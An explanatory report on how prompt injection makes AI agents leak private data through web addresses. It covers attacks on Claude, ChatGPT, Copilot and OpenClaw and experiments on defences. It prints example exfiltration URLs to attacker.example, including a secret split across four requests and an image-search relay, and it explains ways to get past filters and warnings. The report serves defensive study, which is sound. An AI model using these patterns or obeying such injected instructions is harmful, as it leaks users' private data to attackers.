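A setting called `url_sources` lets developers choose which parts of the conversation can supply addresses for Claude to open. They can exclude addresses from user messages, from their own tools, or from searches and fetched pages. The option to exclude their own tools matters because some tools repeat what Claude gives them. For example, if a developer lets Claude run small programs, Claude could write one that prints an address containing Ruth's moving date. The address would then appear in the conversation as the tool's output, so by default Claude could open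 it. Anthropic describes this case and shows developers how to exclude such a tool.

### Spelling out a name by following links

Ayush Paul found a different way around the rule in the Claude app and published it on 9 July 2026 as *The Memory Heist*. At the time, Claude could open links it found on pages it had already fetched, so the owner of a page could supply as many new addresses as an attack needed.

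Paul built a website that looked like a coffee shop's homepage. *The AI Is Now an Attack Surface* (2026), White Cloud Security's account based on Paul's post, explains that the site checked the name each visitor's software reported. It showed the coffee shop to people, but showed Claude, which identifies itself as Claude-User, a fake bot check where AI assistants supposedly had to give their user's name.

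Claude couldn't put the user's name into an address, so the page's instructions had it spell out the name by following links. *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026) describes how the instructions told Claude to find the user's profile by going through the site one letter at a time, and gave the limits of the fetch tool as the reason. The first page had a link for each letter. The page at `/a` linked to `/aa`, `/ab`, `/ac` and so on, and Claude chose the link that continued the name. Paul's server recorded visits to `/a`, `/ay` and `/ayu`, and eventually to `/ayush-paul`.

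This is more convenient for an attacker than ZombieAgent's method, in which each address stood for a single character. Here every address contains all the letters so far, so the last request gives the whole name even if the others arrive out of order or the name has repeated letters.

The attacker also doesn't have to prepare a long list of addresses. Paul's site created each page only when Claude requested it. A ten-character name made from 26 letters and a hyphen allows 27¹⁰, or about 206 trillion, possible addresses. If every page offers 27 links, Claude needs ten visits after the first page and sees 270 links in total. OpenAI's public-index check would refuse nearly all of these addresses, since a crawler could have recorded only the ones it had followed.

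Paul obtained his own name, employer and home city this way, though he hadn't typed any of them into the site. Claude had some of this information in its memory of earlier chats, but it inferred the city from the name of a hackathon Paul had started at school, Queen City Hacks. Queen City is a nickname for Charlotte. A filter that compared outgoing requests with the user's stored details could have missed the city, because its name might not have been among them.

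Paul also suggested that an attacker could write a page about a current news story and get it to rank well in search engines, so that people researching the story would lead Claude to the page. He did not test this.

### Anthropic's fix, and what developers still have to set

Anthropic fixed the vulnerability by stopping the Claude app from opening links it finds on fetched pages. The app can now open only addresses that come from the user or from a web search, so someone who wants Claude to follow a link on a page may have to paste it in.

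Paul had reported the problem through Anthropic's bug bounty programme, but the company didn't pay him because, according to Willison, it had already identified the flaw internally. That is plausible, since the documentation had listed earlier fetch results as a permitted source of addresses since the tool's launch. Anthropic may therefore have known about the route for some time before Paul used it.

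An attacker could still try to leak data by making Claude choose among pages in its search results, the same kind of leak Rehberger described for ChatGPT. The attacker would first have to get enough pages into the search engine and then get Claude to run searches that return them, which is much harder than generating links on demand.

The fix applies to the Claude app. The API still allows links from fetched pages by default, so developers' agents could be vulnerable to Paul's method. Developers can apply the app's stricter rule by using `url_sources` to exclude fetch results. Those whose agents handle private data have good reason to do this, but they have to know the setting exists.

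Anthropic also runs agents for developers on its own servers, in a service called Managed Agents. It didn't get the ban on composed addresses until 7 October 2026, according to Anthropic's *Claude Platform release notes* (2026). That was more than a year after the API tool launched with the same protection. The new rule doesn't accept addresses from attached documents or the output of most tools, but it does accept links from pages that the agent fetched earlier. The Claude app had stopped accepting such links three months before.

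Developers whose agents need only a few sites can avoid most of these problems by giving the tool an allowlist. Since 20 October, administrators have also been able to set a list for their whole organisation or turn web fetch off. In Managed Agents, a redirect's destination must pass the same lists as the original address.

### Microsoft: images from approved sites

Microsoft restricted image loading in Bing Chat in May 2023, seven months before OpenAI introduced url_safe. Its later product for businesses, Microsoft 365 Copilot, uses a content security policy, which is a website's list of the places from which the browser may load content. If Copilot's response includes an image hosted at `attacker.example`, the browser doesn't request it.

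This rule checks only the site's name, so an approved site may still pass the request on to another. url_safe's trusted sites have the same weakness.

That happened with EchoLeak, a zero-click attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that the security company Aim Security disclosed in June 2025. The attacker sent the victim an email containing instructions for Copilot. When the victim later asked about a related subject, Copilot retrieved the email along with confidential material and wrote an image address containing some of that material. The address belonged to Microsoft Teams, which the policy allowed, and a Teams service forwarded the request to the attacker's server. Microsoft fixed the flaw before Aim Security disclosed it.

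### Links that carry the prompt

EchoLeak required the victim to ask Copilot a question. In 2026 Varonis published three attacks on Copilot that required only a click.

The first two used links with a prompt already filled in, like this invented one:

`https://assistant.example/?q=What+is+the+weather+in+Leeds`

Copilot ran the text after `q=` immediately, as though the user had typed it and pressed Enter. An attacker could replace the weather question with a long set of instructions, which would run in the victim's signed-in session.

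Such links are a problem for any rule that trusts the user. If the attacker's text arrives as the user's own message, an address inside it may count as one the user supplied.

Varonis' *Reprompt* describes the first attack, which targeted the personal version of Copilot. Copilot had two defences against leaks through web addresses. It usually opened an address only when given a good reason, and it might remove sensitive data from the address first. The researchers got past the first defence by presenting the request as a small puzzle that Copilot could solve only by opening the address.

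The second defence covered only the first request. The researchers told Copilot to do everything twice and compare the results. On the first attempt Copilot removed their test phrase from the address, but on the second it sent the phrase unchanged. Varonis suspects Microsoft limited the check to save time.

After that, each reply from the attacker's server contained the next instruction, so Copilot sent the user's name, then the time and location, then a summary of the user's last conversation. Someone who examined the original link couldn't have known what the attacker would ask for later. Microsoft patched the flaw in January 2026, and it did not affect business customers using Microsoft 365 Copilot.

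### SearchLeak in three steps

Five months later, Varonis showed that a clicked link could steal data from the business product as well. SearchLeak targeted Copilot's enterprise search, which looks through a worker's email, calendar and company files. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) explains the three weaknesses that it combined:

1. **The link supplied the instructions.** Copilot treated the text after `q=` as a command as well as a search. The attacker's link told it to find an email and put the subject line into the address of an image.
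2. **The browser loaded the image too early.** Microsoft's software made Copilot's answers harmless by turning any web code in them into plain text, but only once the answer was complete. While Copilot was still writing, the browser displayed the unfinished answer and requested the image.
3. **Bing passed the data on.** The content security policy would have blocked an image from the attacker's site, but it allowed images from bing.com. Bing has a feature that searches for pictures similar to one on the web, and to do this its servers fetch the picture from whatever address they receive.

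With invented sites, the address of the image would look like this:

`https://search.example/similar?picture=https://attacker.example/Your-code-is-418302/a.png`

The victim's browser contacts only the search engine, whose server then requests the picture from `attacker.example`. The attacker reads the login code in the log of that request. Many services put login codes in email subject lines, so a subject line alone is often enough to do damage.

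SearchLeak was much faster than Tenable's Bing attack on ChatGPT, which needed a separate link for every letter. The image search accepted any address, so SearchLeak could send a whole subject line in one request. OpenAI's exact lookup would have rejected the address in that request.

The victim might have noticed Copilot giving an odd answer, but by then the data had already been stolen. Phishing filters were little help because the link led to Microsoft. Microsoft rated the flaw critical and patched it in June 2026, according to TechRadar's *Microsoft 365 Copilot can be turned into a one-click data theft tool*. Varonis advises companies to treat any approved site that fetches web addresses for other people as a possible route for data theft. That advice would also have applied to the Teams service used in EchoLeak a year earlier.

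The third attack, CoSnitch, also began with a click on a legitimate-looking link. According to Varonis' *CoSnitch*, Microsoft received the report in December 2025 and released the patch on 18 August 2026, about eight months later.

### A prepared link for Claude

Claude had a similar problem. Oasis Security's *Claudy Day* describes a link that filled in the chat box on claude.ai with an ordinary question and added instructions in invisible HTML tags. The user had to press Enter to run the prompt, but few people would hesitate to do that when the question looked harmless.

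The researchers also found a way to spread the link without sending it to anyone. Anthropic's claude.com site would redirect visitors to other addresses, so an attacker could create a Google search result that looked identical to Claude's real one but led to the prepared chat.

The attack got the data out through the restricted environment where Claude runs code, without needing the fetch tool. That environment could reach Anthropic's own file storage service. The hidden instructions included an access key for the attacker's Anthropic account, and Claude uploaded the user's conversation history to that account. Rehberger had collected data from ChatGPT in much the same way, through a Microsoft storage account.

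Anthropic had fixed the hidden-instruction problem and was still working on the others when TechNadu's *The Claudy Day Vulnerability Chains Prompt Injection, Open Redirects, and Data Exfiltration* appeared.

### Link previews in messaging apps

Some people talk to their agents through messaging apps such as Slack or Telegram. When a message contains a link, these apps usually load the page to show its title and a small picture. If an agent wrote the link, that request can send the user's data to an attacker before the user has read the message.

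PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* demonstrated this risk in February 2026 with OpenClaw, a popular agent that people can use through apps like Telegram. Hidden instructions in something the agent reads make it add a link to its reply, with private data in the address. Without link previews, the user would have to click the link to send the data, but with OpenClaw's default Telegram settings, the preview sent it as soon as the agent replied.

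Suppose Ruth's agent sends her its comparison of removal firms on Telegram, ending with a link to a full quote. If the link contains her moving date, the attacker has the date even if she finds the link suspicious and doesn't click it.

A rule about what the agent may open doesn't prevent this, because the agent only writes text and the messaging app makes the request. OpenClaw users can turn off previews for Telegram by adding `linkPreview: false` to a settings file, and PromptArmor found that this stopped the leak. But users have to make this change themselves, and most have probably never thought of a preview as a security risk.

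PromptArmor set up a website where people can test their own combination of agent and app. The site records any preview request and the data sent with it. In the published example, the record contained a name and an access key. PromptArmor wants messaging companies to let people turn off link previews for particular chats, so that they can give an agent a safe channel and still see previews in chats with friends.

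### Google

Google's URL context tool lets developers have Gemini models read web pages by putting the addresses in the prompt. If the developer also turns on Google Search, Gemini can find pages by searching and then read them in full, according to Google's documentation, *URL context*. *Platform Comparisons*, rhyannonjoy's comparison of such tools, adds that the addresses must be complete and "unnested", which suggests that Gemini reads the pages it is given without following their links.

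If so, Google's tool takes addresses from roughly the same places as the Claude app has since Paul's report, and a site like his would have trouble leading Gemini from page to page. Google's tool would also share the weakness Willison saw in Anthropic's, since a developer can paste a stranger's email into the prompt.

These rules are for a developer tool, and other Google products work differently. In 2025 PromptArmor showed that a web page with hidden instructions could make Gemini leak data from Antigravity, Google's programming environment. Willison (2025) recorded in *41 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* that the page was disguised as a guide for programmers, and that Gemini collected passwords and code from the user's project and sent them out.

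### The products compared

| Product | Whose addresses it accepts | Published way round | Fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT, since the public-index check | An independent crawler's and, as Rehberger understands it, the user's | Spelling out a secret by choosing among public pages, which Rehberger described but did not demonstrate | No complete fix announced; Lockdown Mode should prevent it |
| Claude app | The user's and those from web searches | Paul's nested links | By mid-July 2026, Claude stopped opening links from fetched pages |
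| Claude API | Any in user messages, developers' tools, searches or fetched pages | A tool that repeats an address Claude wrote, as Anthropic itself warns | Developers can exclude each source |
| Copilot, personal version | Anyone's, if Copilot accepted the reason for opening it | Reprompt | Patched in January 2026 |
| Microsoft 365 Copilot, images | Anyone's, if the site is on Microsoft's list | EchoLeak and SearchLeak | Patched in 2025 and June 2026 |
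| OpenClaw with Telegram | Anyone's, because Telegram requests the preview | A link with private data in the agent's reply | Users can turn previews off |
| Gemini API, URL context | The developer's prompt and, if turned on, Google Search | None reported for this tool; the Antigravity leak involved a different product | Not applicable |

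## Which defences work in experiments?

OpenAI uses several defences at once, so when an attack on ChatGPT fails, outsiders can't easily tell what stopped it. Researchers can learn more by building their own agent, giving it an invented secret and changing one thing at a time. In the four studies most relevant to leaks through web requests, warnings and training often made fewer attacks succeed. Strict limits on where the agent could send data stopped every attack, but the test conditions suited those limits.

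### An agent with no defences

In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) at eBay measured how often an unprotected agent would leak private data. They used qwen2.5:7b, a small open model with about seven billion weights. The researchers put made-up private data in its prompt and asked it to summarise a web page. The software around the model fetched the page and added its title, description and text to the prompt. That material included an instruction to send the data to another address, presented as a routine check.

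The researchers ran 480 trials, 30 for each combination of four hiding places, two ways of reaching the page and two ways of sending the data. The agent contacted the attacker's server in 423 trials, or 88 percent. In 95 percent of the successful attacks, the answer on the screen looked harmless. In 120 trials with clean pages, the agent never contacted that server.

We can't infer much from these rates about commercial products. The model was far weaker than the ones behind ChatGPT, the private data was in plain view, and the agent's standing instructions covered only how to use its tools. Lan and colleagues chose conditions that favoured the attacker to get a clear baseline. They also used blunt injections, and argue that stronger models might do worse because such models follow instructions more reliably. Results from other experiments are mixed and depend heavily on how the attack is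 worded.

### Warning the model

The easiest defence to add is a warning in the system prompt, the instructions a developer gives a model before the user's first message. Lan and colleagues told the model to treat web content as data and to follow only the user. Leaks fell from 100 percent of trials to 67 percent (20 of 30). When they instead put tags around the page's text to mark it as untrusted, the agent still leaked every time. With both the warning and the tags, it leaked in 57 percent of trials (17 of 30), but the difference from the warning alone could easily be chance.

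Warnings worked better in *INFUSE* (Nguyen, Guo and colleagues, 2026), which tested 19 models as agents that work by typing commands on a computer. The attacks included stealing passwords, corrupting files and installing untrustworthy software. On a set of cases where attacks worked unusually well, stricter instructions reduced the success rate from 58.2 percent to 14.3 percent. Separate safety filters made for chatbots left it at about 44 percent. The stricter instructions also made some models worse at their ordinary tasks.

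A warning that works on one model may do little for another, or may fail against a persistent attacker. *Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary* (2026) reports that warnings reduced successful attacks on OpenAI's GPT-4.1-mini from 100 percent to 1 percent in tests of 100 trials each. In another test, a second model repeatedly reworded the attack without seeing the warning. Within 50 attempts, it found a version that worked every time against the best single warning for GPT-4.1-mini. That version later stopped working, and the researchers couldn't determine why.

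### Models trained to refuse

*Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration* (Rall, Bauer and colleagues, 2025) compared 28 models in the same agent, with no protection beyond each model's training. The agent could open web pages and search a company's internal documents, which contained a secret about a fictional Project Alpha. When the user asked for a summary of a blog post, the agent also read white text on the page's white background. The hidden text instructed the agent to look up the secret and request a web address containing it.

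The researchers started with 89 attack texts, some of them public since 2023. They made 11 altered versions of each, for example by rewording it, translating it into Hindi or encoding it. Each model faced all 1,068 attacks once, including the originals.

xAI's Grok 4 leaked the secret in 72.4 percent of them. The next highest rate was 29.1 percent, for Inception's Mercury. Six models never leaked it, including Anthropic's Claude Sonnet 4 and OpenAI's GPT-5 nano. Altering the attacks generally made them less effective, because the model also had to work out what the altered text meant. No model followed instructions written in binary code.

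Larger models weren't consistently safer. Hermes 4's leak rate fell from 6.0 percent with 70 billion weights to 0.1 percent with about 405 billion, while Qwen3's rose from 8.2 percent with 32 billion to 28.3 percent with 235 billion.

Rall and colleagues attribute the differences mainly to training. OpenAI, for example, trains its models to rank instructions by their source, giving text returned by a tool less authority than a user's request. This explanation is plausible, but the study compared finished products, not the same model with and without that training. Some weaker models may also have scored well because they couldn't complete the steps.

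*Domain-Conditioned Safety in Frontier Computer-Using Agents* (2026), a later study, provides better evidence that the model itself can resist attacks. Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GPT-5.4 each resisted all 16 attacks in one round of browser tests. Sonnet 4.6 also resisted in 24 further trials with different system prompts, including one that told it to follow any instructions it saw on a page, so the prompt wasn't what protected it.

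### Why rewording an attack works

A score of zero against known attacks can be misleading. *The Framing Gap* shows this with GPT-4o, a 2024 OpenAI model. The test agent held a secret token and was forbidden to send it anywhere except one trusted site. It read a web page and then took one action, such as sending data to an address. The sending tool only recorded each attempt, so nothing left the researchers' computer. An attack counted as successful only if the agent leaked the token after reading the malicious page but not after reading a clean one.

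GPT-4o leaked nothing when tested on ten ordinary kinds of injection, with 20 trials each. The researchers then changed how the page described the leak. Some new pages presented the secret token as a necessary part of a routine request, such as a checksum (a short code used to detect errors) or a configuration value. Others made the attacker's address look like the trusted one. None of the new pages asked the agent to disclose a secret. GPT-4o sent the token in every trial with the two most effective versions, and in 40 percent of trials across all eight versions, including an unchanged one for comparison. Five of the six models in the study leaked much more often after the rewording.

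The researchers concluded that GPT-4o had taken the page's demands as part of its task. They removed the secrecy rule to check whether the attack was overcoming it. Leaks rose only from 31.9 percent to 38.1 percent, so the rule had prevented few leaks. The page's wording mattered more, since GPT-4o didn't send the token when the page called it a credential, such as a password or access key.

An attacker can find an effective wording with little effort. Across five paraphrases of the checksum story, the success rate ranged from 0 to 100 percent. The researchers calculated that an attacker who tried three of them would succeed about 96 percent of the time. Finding a new pretext that worked was much harder. The researchers wrote 13 pages around new pretexts, and none produced a leak in 130 trials.

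A more thorough rule stopped the reworded attacks. It barred GPT-4o from signing, encoding, logging, appending or transmitting the token "in any form", and the model leaked nothing in 120 trials. Without the words "in any form", it leaked in 39 of 80 trials.

The researchers tested SecAlign, a published method for training models to ignore instructions in outside text, on Meta's Llama 3.1 8B. The trained model resisted all 20 attempts at a standard injection that always worked on the ordinary model. With the reworded attacks, however, it leaked in 32.5 percent of trials, compared with 21.2 percent for the ordinary model. The researchers ran each test once and don't claim that SecAlign made things worse. SecAlign's training also focused on text answers, and it wasn't made for agents with tools like the one tested here.

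Skilled people who keep changing their attacks can also get past newer models, though less often. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) analysed a public competition in which 464 participants made 272,000 attempts on 13 leading models. Participants had to make the agent do something harmful without revealing the attack in its final answer. Success rates ranged from 0.5 percent against Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5 percent against Gemini 2.5 Pro. If each attempt had an independent 0.5 percent chance, an attacker would have a better than even chance of succeeding at least once after 139 attempts, a number that is easy to send by email.

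### Why did ChatGPT hold when GPT-4o leaked?

*The Framing Gap* also tested its attacks on the ChatGPT product. The researchers put a made-up secret in a chat on their own account and asked ChatGPT to summarise public pages containing the attacks. ChatGPT did not reveal the secret in any of 48 valid trials, although GPT-4o, used through the API, had leaked in up to 100 percent of trials with some of the same attacks. With so few trials, the product's true leak rate could still be as high as 7.4 percent.

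The study doesn't establish why ChatGPT resisted the attack. OpenAI may have been using a different model, removing suspicious text from pages, running a separate detector or giving the model stricter instructions. In one variant, ChatGPT refused to reveal the secret and described what it had found on the page as a placeholder. The researchers take this as a sign that a classifier had checked the incoming page, but a well-trained model could give the same answer without one.

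The comparison was also uneven because the API agent could send data to an outside address, whereas the ChatGPT test counted a leak only if the secret appeared in the reply. Secrets in replies may be easier to catch. The result therefore can't show whether Safe Url would have stopped a leak through a web request.

### Filters, encoding and split secrets

A filter can search each outgoing request for the secret, whatever persuaded the agent to send it, but it can miss a secret that the agent has disguised. *The Framing Gap* tested pages that asked GPT-4o to disguise the token, and a filter for the exact token reduced leaks only from 56.7 percent to 50.0 percent. Writing the token backwards got it past the filter every time.

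The researchers then built a better filter that reversed the disguises they expected, and it stopped all of them. But it failed in every trial with ROT13, a simple code that replaces each letter with the one 13 places along in the alphabet. An attacker can get past this kind of filter with any code that the model can write and the filter's designer didn't anticipate.

Lan and colleagues tested splitting, in which the agent divides a secret into pieces and sends each in a separate request. Suppose the secret is Ruth's street and moving date, written as `22-Elm-Road-14-March`. The agent could request four invented addresses:

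`https://attacker.example/collect?part=0&total=4&data=22-El`  
`https://attacker.example/collect?part=1&total=4&data=m-Roa`  
`https://attacker.example/collect?part=2&total=4&data=d-14-`  
`https://attacker.example/collect?part=3&total=4&data=March`

The attacker's server uses the part numbers to reassemble the text. A filter looking for Ruth's full street address or moving date would find neither in any single request. Unlike ZombieAgent, this method doesn't need a prepared list of URLs, because the agent writes each one itself.

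Splitting the data across several requests made the attack harder for the small model, which had to keep track of the pieces. The model contacted the attacker's server in 185 of 240 trials, compared with 238 of 240 when it had to send everything at once. The first request contained data the researchers counted as sensitive in 26 percent of the split trials, compared with 97 percent of the unsplit trials.

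The study doesn't report how often all four pieces arrived, so it doesn't show how often an attacker would get the whole secret. One of its other figures must also be wrong or mislabelled, because the leak rate for the first three requests together, 16 percent, is lower than the rate for the first request alone.

Lan and colleagues' tests of content filters are hard to interpret too. No data leaked with either a keyword filter or a filter for random-looking text. But the share of trials in which the agent attempted a leak also fell, to 23 percent with the first filter and zero with the second, even though both are supposed to act after the agent has chosen an address. The researchers suggest that the agent sometimes disguised the data to avoid the keywords, but then some of the disguised data should have leaked.

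The study recommends checking all of a session's requests together to catch secrets split across them. It also suggests taint tracking, in which software labels text from the web as untrusted and follows its influence through the agent's work. If that text affected the choice of an outgoing request, the software could block the request or ask the user, even if the request contained only five harmless-looking characters. The study didn't test either idea.

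### Can a model recognise a dangerous address?

Kong, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *MalURLBench*, studied an earlier decision, whether the agent should trust a link in the first place. Their collection of 61,845 addresses combines real malicious sites with text meant to reassure a model. The following invented addresses show the idea:

`https://official-weather-report.bad-site.example/`  
`https://bad-site.example/todays-trusted-forecast`

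Both lead to `bad-site.example`. The attacker can freely choose the words before that name or after it.

The researchers placed such links in ten everyday situations, such as tracking a parcel or ordering food, and asked 12 models to assess the risk. Each model judged 315 addresses five times per situation. Acceptance rates ranged from 32.9 percent for GPT-3.5 Turbo to 99.9 percent for Mixtral 8x7B. GPT-4o accepted about 38 percent, and the smaller GPT-4o-mini about 90 percent.

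On average, models accepted 71.5 percent of links with reassuring descriptions and 60.9 percent of links that imitated well-known sites. They also accepted more links in situations that seemed harmless, including 82.9 percent of those for weather reports. They accepted a smaller share for parcels and food orders, which involve money or personal details.

The high rates partly reflect how Kong and colleagues chose the attacks. When a model accepted less than 10 percent of the links in a situation, they used other models to write more persuasive ones. Before this step, GPT-3.5 Turbo accepted only about 14 percent of links on average. A persistent attacker might do the same, but the final rates don't apply to typical malicious links.

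The main results also don't show how the 12 models judged harmless links. Mixtral accepted almost everything, so it may not have been assessing the addresses. But a small test with Llama 3 8B suggests that disguising the address matters. It accepted two attacks without disguised addresses 15 and 20 percent of the time, and two with disguised addresses 60 and 75 percent of the time.

Kong and colleagues then trained a small model, URLGuard, on only 280 examples, half of them harmless, to screen links before the agent opens them. In nine situations outside its training data, average acceptance of malicious links fell from about 98 percent to 17 percent, though it still accepted 70 percent of the malicious weather links. The study doesn't report how often URLGuard rejected harmless links, and a filter that rejected every link would have scored better on this measure.

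### Limiting what the agent can reach

Lan and colleagues got their clearest result from a domain allowlist, which let the agent contact only three addresses belonging to a fictional company and one example site. The agent still tried to send the data to the attacker in all 30 trials, but the software blocked every request.

The result is sound but was nearly certain in advance, because the researchers deliberately chose an attacker's site that was not on the list. They didn't test an attacker who had taken over an approved site or found a redirect on one, though they acknowledge that both could happen in practice.

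*The Framing Gap* tested another kind of limit, which splits the agent in two. A planner decides what to do without access to the web page, and a reader summarises the page without access to the secret token. Hostile instructions can reach only the reader, which has nothing to leak. The token did not leak in any of the 80 trials with reworded attacks or the 30 that used codes like ROT13. The agent still produced a good summary of nine out of ten clean pages.

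Summarising a page suits this design because the planner doesn't need the page's contents. Ruth's task would be harder. One removal firm's page might show that her agent should open another page for prices, but a planner without access to the first page couldn't make that choice. The researchers note that similar designs have lost much more usefulness on tasks like this in other tests.

Limits can also miss information that leaks through an agent's ordinary browsing. Liang and colleagues tested four existing defences against SNOOP, their attack that infers a user's interests from the pages an agent chooses. Spotlighting marks outside text as untrusted, Firewalls filters what goes into and out of tools, Task Shield checks actions against the user's request, and Fides restricts where sensitive information can flow. None reduced SNOOP's score by more than 0.03 on a scale from 0 to 1. The agent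 was opening relevant pages for a legitimate task, and no request contained private text for the defences to find.

### Training or limits?

The table compares the main defences. Each row shows results with and without the defence for the same model and attacks, but the models and attacks differ between some rows.

| Defence | Study | Leaks without it | Leaks with it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Warning in the system prompt | Lan and colleagues | 100% | 67% |
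| Tags around untrusted text | Lan and colleagues | 100% | 100% |
| Secrecy rule covering "any form" | *The Framing Gap*, GPT-4o | 31.9% | 0% |
| The same rule without that phrase | *The Framing Gap*, GPT-4o | 31.9% | 48.8% |
| SecAlign training | *The Framing Gap*, Llama 3.1 8B | 21.2% | 32.5% |
| Filter for the exact secret, disguised token | *The Framing Gap*, GPT-4o | 56.7% | 50.0% |
| Separate planner and reader | *The Framing Gap*, Llama 3.1 8B | 21.2% | 0% |
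| Domain allowlist | Lan and colleagues | 100% | 0% |

Training is still worthwhile. In Rall and colleagues' tests, Grok 4 leaked and six other models never did, so a developer can gain a lot by choosing a more resistant model. But that resistance applies to the attacks in the test. GPT-4o went from never leaking to leaking every time when the researchers described the same request differently.

An allowlist works the same way however the attacker words the request, which supports OpenAI's argument for limiting the damage when a model is fooled. But the four studies don't measure how such limits affect ordinary use. Neither allowlist test measured how many useful requests the list would block for someone who searches the whole web.

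None of the four studies tests a public-index check. Such a check should stop the web requests in the experiments by Lan and colleagues and by Rall and colleagues, because the agent puts the secret into an address that no crawler has recorded. It should also stop the split version, since each of the four addresses is new. In *The Framing Gap*, the agent could send the token as data separate from the URL, so checking only the URL could miss it. In MalURLBench, the link comes from the user, and ChatGPT apparently opens addresses that users supply.

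The studies also leave out the attack that Rehberger considers possible against OpenAI's check, in which the agent spells out a secret by choosing among public pages. To test the check against this attack, researchers would need to give the attacker pages the crawler has already recorded and count how many harmless requests trigger a warning.

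## Have such attacks happened outside research?

Attackers have tried to manipulate AI agents outside the laboratory, but there is little public evidence that they have stolen data this way. In 2026 Google, Microsoft, several security companies and a group of academics all found instructions for AI systems on live web pages or in links sent by email. Only a few of the instructions were requests for private data, and none of their reports describes a real victim whose agent leaked data through a web address. According to the security company Darktrace's article *Comment les attaques par injection de prompt transmises par email peuvent cibler* (2026), there were only a handful of known victims of any kind of prompt injection.

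Researchers demonstrated with ShadowLeak, ZombieAgent and SearchLeak that a leak was possible. A hostile page on the live web is evidence of an attempted attack, but it does not establish that data was stolen from a real victim.

### What scans of the web have found

The most detailed count comes from Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*. They searched 1.2 billion web addresses, about half of the October 2025 edition of Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages. Their software looked for 3,963 phrases typical of prompt injection, such as orders to ignore earlier instructions. Many matches came from tutorials and articles about prompt injection, so the researchers reviewed the matches and kept only text actually addressed to an AI system.

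Together with about 3,300 results from two services that scan internet-connected computers, this gave 15,387 confirmed injections on 11,722 pages. In Common Crawl alone, about eight in every million pages contained one. Most of the people who wrote the injections wanted to disrupt AI systems or keep them away, as the table shows. An injection can count towards more than one aim.

| Aim | Injections |
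|---|---|
| Disrupt the AI, mostly by making it produce nonsense | 8,894 |
| Protect personal information or copyright | 4,093 |
| Detect AI visitors | 3,096 |
| Replace the AI's task, for no clear purpose | 2,632 |
| Promote a product, person or website | 1,521 |
| Obtain hidden data | 13 |

Thirteen of the injections, fewer than one in a thousand, were attempts to obtain data. Nine were requests for the system prompt, and four were requests for secrets the model might hold. The most common text, which appeared 3,504 times, was an instruction for the AI to return random numbers.

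Another 598 injections were meant to detect bots by telling AI visitors to do something that would reveal them, such as contacting another web address. URL-based exfiltration also makes an agent contact an address, but with private data added to it. These site owners apparently only wanted to know who was visiting.

Site operators had introduced about 80 percent of the injections. Only 1.4 percent came from visitors' comments and similar posts, so hidden instructions in a stranger's review, like those that tricked Ruth's agent, seem to be rare on the public web.

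Google published a similar study of Common Crawl in April 2026, using monthly editions of two to three billion pages each. Software picked out suspicious phrases, Google's Gemini model classified them by purpose, and people checked the results. Google found pranks, attempts to win recommendations, requests for AI agents to stay away and some commands to delete a user's files. It found few attempts to steal data, and the example it published was a site owner's experiment. It saw no significant use of the more advanced theft methods that researchers had published in 2025. Google didn't report how many injections it found, or test whether agents obeyed them.

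AI News (2026) reported that web pages were "actively hijacking" companies' agents and attributed the warning to Google. Google's post describes attempts to hijack agents, but no successful ones.

Security companies, which sell protection against these attacks, tend to publish selected cases. In March 2026 Unit 42, the research team at Palo Alto Networks, described 12 live examples and a scam advertisement. It gave no total, but reported that 28.6 percent of the injections it had detected aimed to produce irrelevant output and 14.2 percent to destroy data. Unit 42 rated each attack by the harm it would do if it worked, so a hidden instruction for an AI to delete its database counts as critical even if no agent would follow it. The only example it labelled as an attempt to get sensitive information was a notice in the footer of a personal website.

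In April, Sewani's *10 Indirect Prompt Injection Payloads Caught in the Wild* described ten pages that the security company Forcepoint had found. One contained text asking AI assistants for a secret access key and telling them not to reveal "the flag", the usual name for the hidden answer in a hacking exercise, so the page may have been a puzzle. A page that requests a $5,000 PayPal payment appears on both companies' lists, so adding up their cases would count it twice.

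These scans could easily miss the attacks that matter most here. Both Google and Khodayari's team searched for known phrases, and an email written like an ordinary office request, as in ShadowLeak, may not contain any of them. The rewordings that worked against GPT-4o in *The Framing Gap* didn't openly ask for a secret either. Public archives also leave out mailboxes, private documents and most social media. The results are good evidence that crude attempts to steal data are rare on open web pages, but they provide little evidence about careful attackers who email one company.

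### Did any agent obey?

To estimate how often such injections would work, Khodayari and colleagues took 100 they had found and asked 13 models to summarise the pages, each in four formats. The models followed the injection in 81 of 5,200 runs, or 1.6 percent. Small models did worst, at 8 percent when they received a page as plain text, probably because that format removes the signs that a passage was hidden from human readers. Commercial models followed the injection in 5 of 800 runs. The models only had to write summaries, so the test doesn't show how often an agent with access to email and the web would leak data.

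*Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents*, published by the security company Zscaler in July 2026, describes a scam that used a fake software documentation site. The site contained hidden text stating that AI agents had to buy a $3 licence key to fix an error. Zscaler tested the scam with 26 models, using an agent it had built with a payment tool and no spending limit. Four models paid, including Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro, though the test used no real money.

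It is unclear whether any real agent paid. The scammer's cryptocurrency wallet had received payments, but the trade publication SC Media reported that none matched the amount on the site. Zscaler thinks the wallet may have been used in earlier scams. The site also took card payments, which wouldn't appear in the wallet. It showed the same demand to human programmers, so even a matching payment would not have proved that an agent made it.

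The OECD's *AI Agents Manipulated by Hidden Web Prompts to Make Fraudulent Payments* (2026), an AI-generated entry in a database of AI incidents, states that the attacks caused unauthorised payments and financial losses, but Zscaler's report does not establish either.

It is also unclear whether the scam advertisement that Unit 42 found ever fooled an AI reviewer. The page sold "military glasses" with a fake discount, and its code contained many hidden attempts to persuade an AI reviewer to approve the advertisement. Unit 42 knew of no confirmed case of this working on an advertisement checker in actual use.

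### Links that write to an assistant's memory

The best-documented use of hostile links is in marketing. In February, Microsoft (2026) described company websites with a button for summarising the page with AI. The button opens the visitor's assistant with a prompt already filled in, as in Varonis' Reprompt attack. The prompt contains a request for the summary, but also an instruction to remember the company as a trusted source. If the assistant saves that instruction, it may favour the company in later chats.

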